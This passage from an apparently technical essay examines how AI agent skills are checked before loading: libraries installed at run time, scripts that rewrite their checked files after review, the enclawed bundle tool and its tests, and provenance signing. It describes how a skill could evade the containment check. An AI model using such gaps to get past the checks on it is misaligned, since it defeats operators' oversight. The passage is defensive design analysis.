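Even a correct proof checker cannot detect a mistake in the specification. Symbolic Software (2026) reports three bugs in libcrux, a cryptographic library whose developer, Cryspen, uses formal verification. Two were in the mathematical specification of ML-KEM, a method for agreeing on encryption keys, and the third was in a correctness proof that the documentation described as complete. Symbolic Software and Cryspen are in a public dispute, and Cryspen had said that nobody had found bugs in its verified code. A wrong entry in a skill analyser's table of library effects would pose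 a similar risk, because every proof would rely on that table.

### Code that arrives or changes after the check

Some runtimes install a script's libraries only when the script runs. With *skill mcp*, a server that runs skills' scripts, a script's author lists the required packages inside the Python script. When the agent starts the script, the server reads the list, creates a separate environment and installs the packages. The load-time analysis cannot read the packages' code, because they are not yet installed. The installer also contacts the network, even if the script never does.

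To close this gap, the author can list an exact version and hash for each package. The runtime downloads the packages before step 3, checks them against the hashes and includes their code in the analysis. The script then runs in an environment where nothing more can be installed.

The skill's own files could also change after the check. Metere's rule against unapproved edits requires the runtime to log each edit the agent attempts, with hashes of the content before and after, even if the operator refuses it. Loading another skill requires a restart.

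This rule can catch an edit that the agent requests through an envelope, but it can miss an edit by a script, which writes to the disk directly. Suppose a script with permission to write in its own folder replaces `fetch.py` after the runtime has checked it. The next time the agent starts `fetch.py`, Python reads the new version. The runtime can prevent this by copying the checked files to a folder that scripts cannot change and running them only from there.

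### What enclawed ships and what its tests establish

enclawed includes a command-line program that produces a bundle. It reads the manifest from a `skill.json` file or from SKILL.md, runs the three default methods and writes the four files. A small demonstration skill lets a developer try the whole process.

If the user supplies no signing key, the program creates a temporary one. This is enough for a demonstration, but a runtime should reject a bundle signed with it at step 2, because the temporary key is not on the runtime's list of trusted keys.

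Some of enclawed's 53 tests concern the bundle. They check that:

- a bundle from an authorised signer passes and one from an unauthorised signer fails;
- the re-checker notices changes to each evidence file;
- the re-checker reports a mismatch when the skill has changed since someone produced the bundle.

All 53 tests pass, which is good evidence that the re-checker detects these kinds of tampering. They do not show that a skill with a valid bundle stays within *D*, because none of the listed tests compares a script's real effects with the scanner's result. Metere also lists no test in which the gate's policy changes while *D* and *K* stay the same.

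Two file names in enclawed's default bundles could mislead an operator, because `types.proof.json` contains no proof from a type checker and `smt.unsat.json` contains no output from an SMT solver. Bundles also receive the same label, "formal", whether they were made with the default scanner or a sound analyser. But the signed statement names the tools, so an operator could accept only bundles from tools they consider strong enough.

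### Signatures that establish provenance

Other systems record software's provenance, or where it came from. Sigstore is a service for signing software, and SLSA is a set of levels for how well a producer documents and protects the build process. They can show that a package came from a particular source and that nobody altered it on the way, but as Metere points out, a malicious skill can have a SLSA attestation as good as a harmless one's.

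Some skill catalogues offer a simpler form of this evidence. Bernstein's *Skill catalog with signed manifest installs* describes a catalogue that stores a hash of each skill and an optional signature, so an operator can show exactly which files were installed. The operator can override the check with `--allow-unverified`.

Provenance can still support a containment proof by helping an operator confirm that the analyser is the audited version and that the installed libraries are the ones the analyser examined. An operator who does not want to repeat the analysis could also accept a signed record that a trusted build service ran it on these exact files. That would make loading faster, but the operator would have to trust the service, and Necula's method was meant to make that kind of trust unnecessary.
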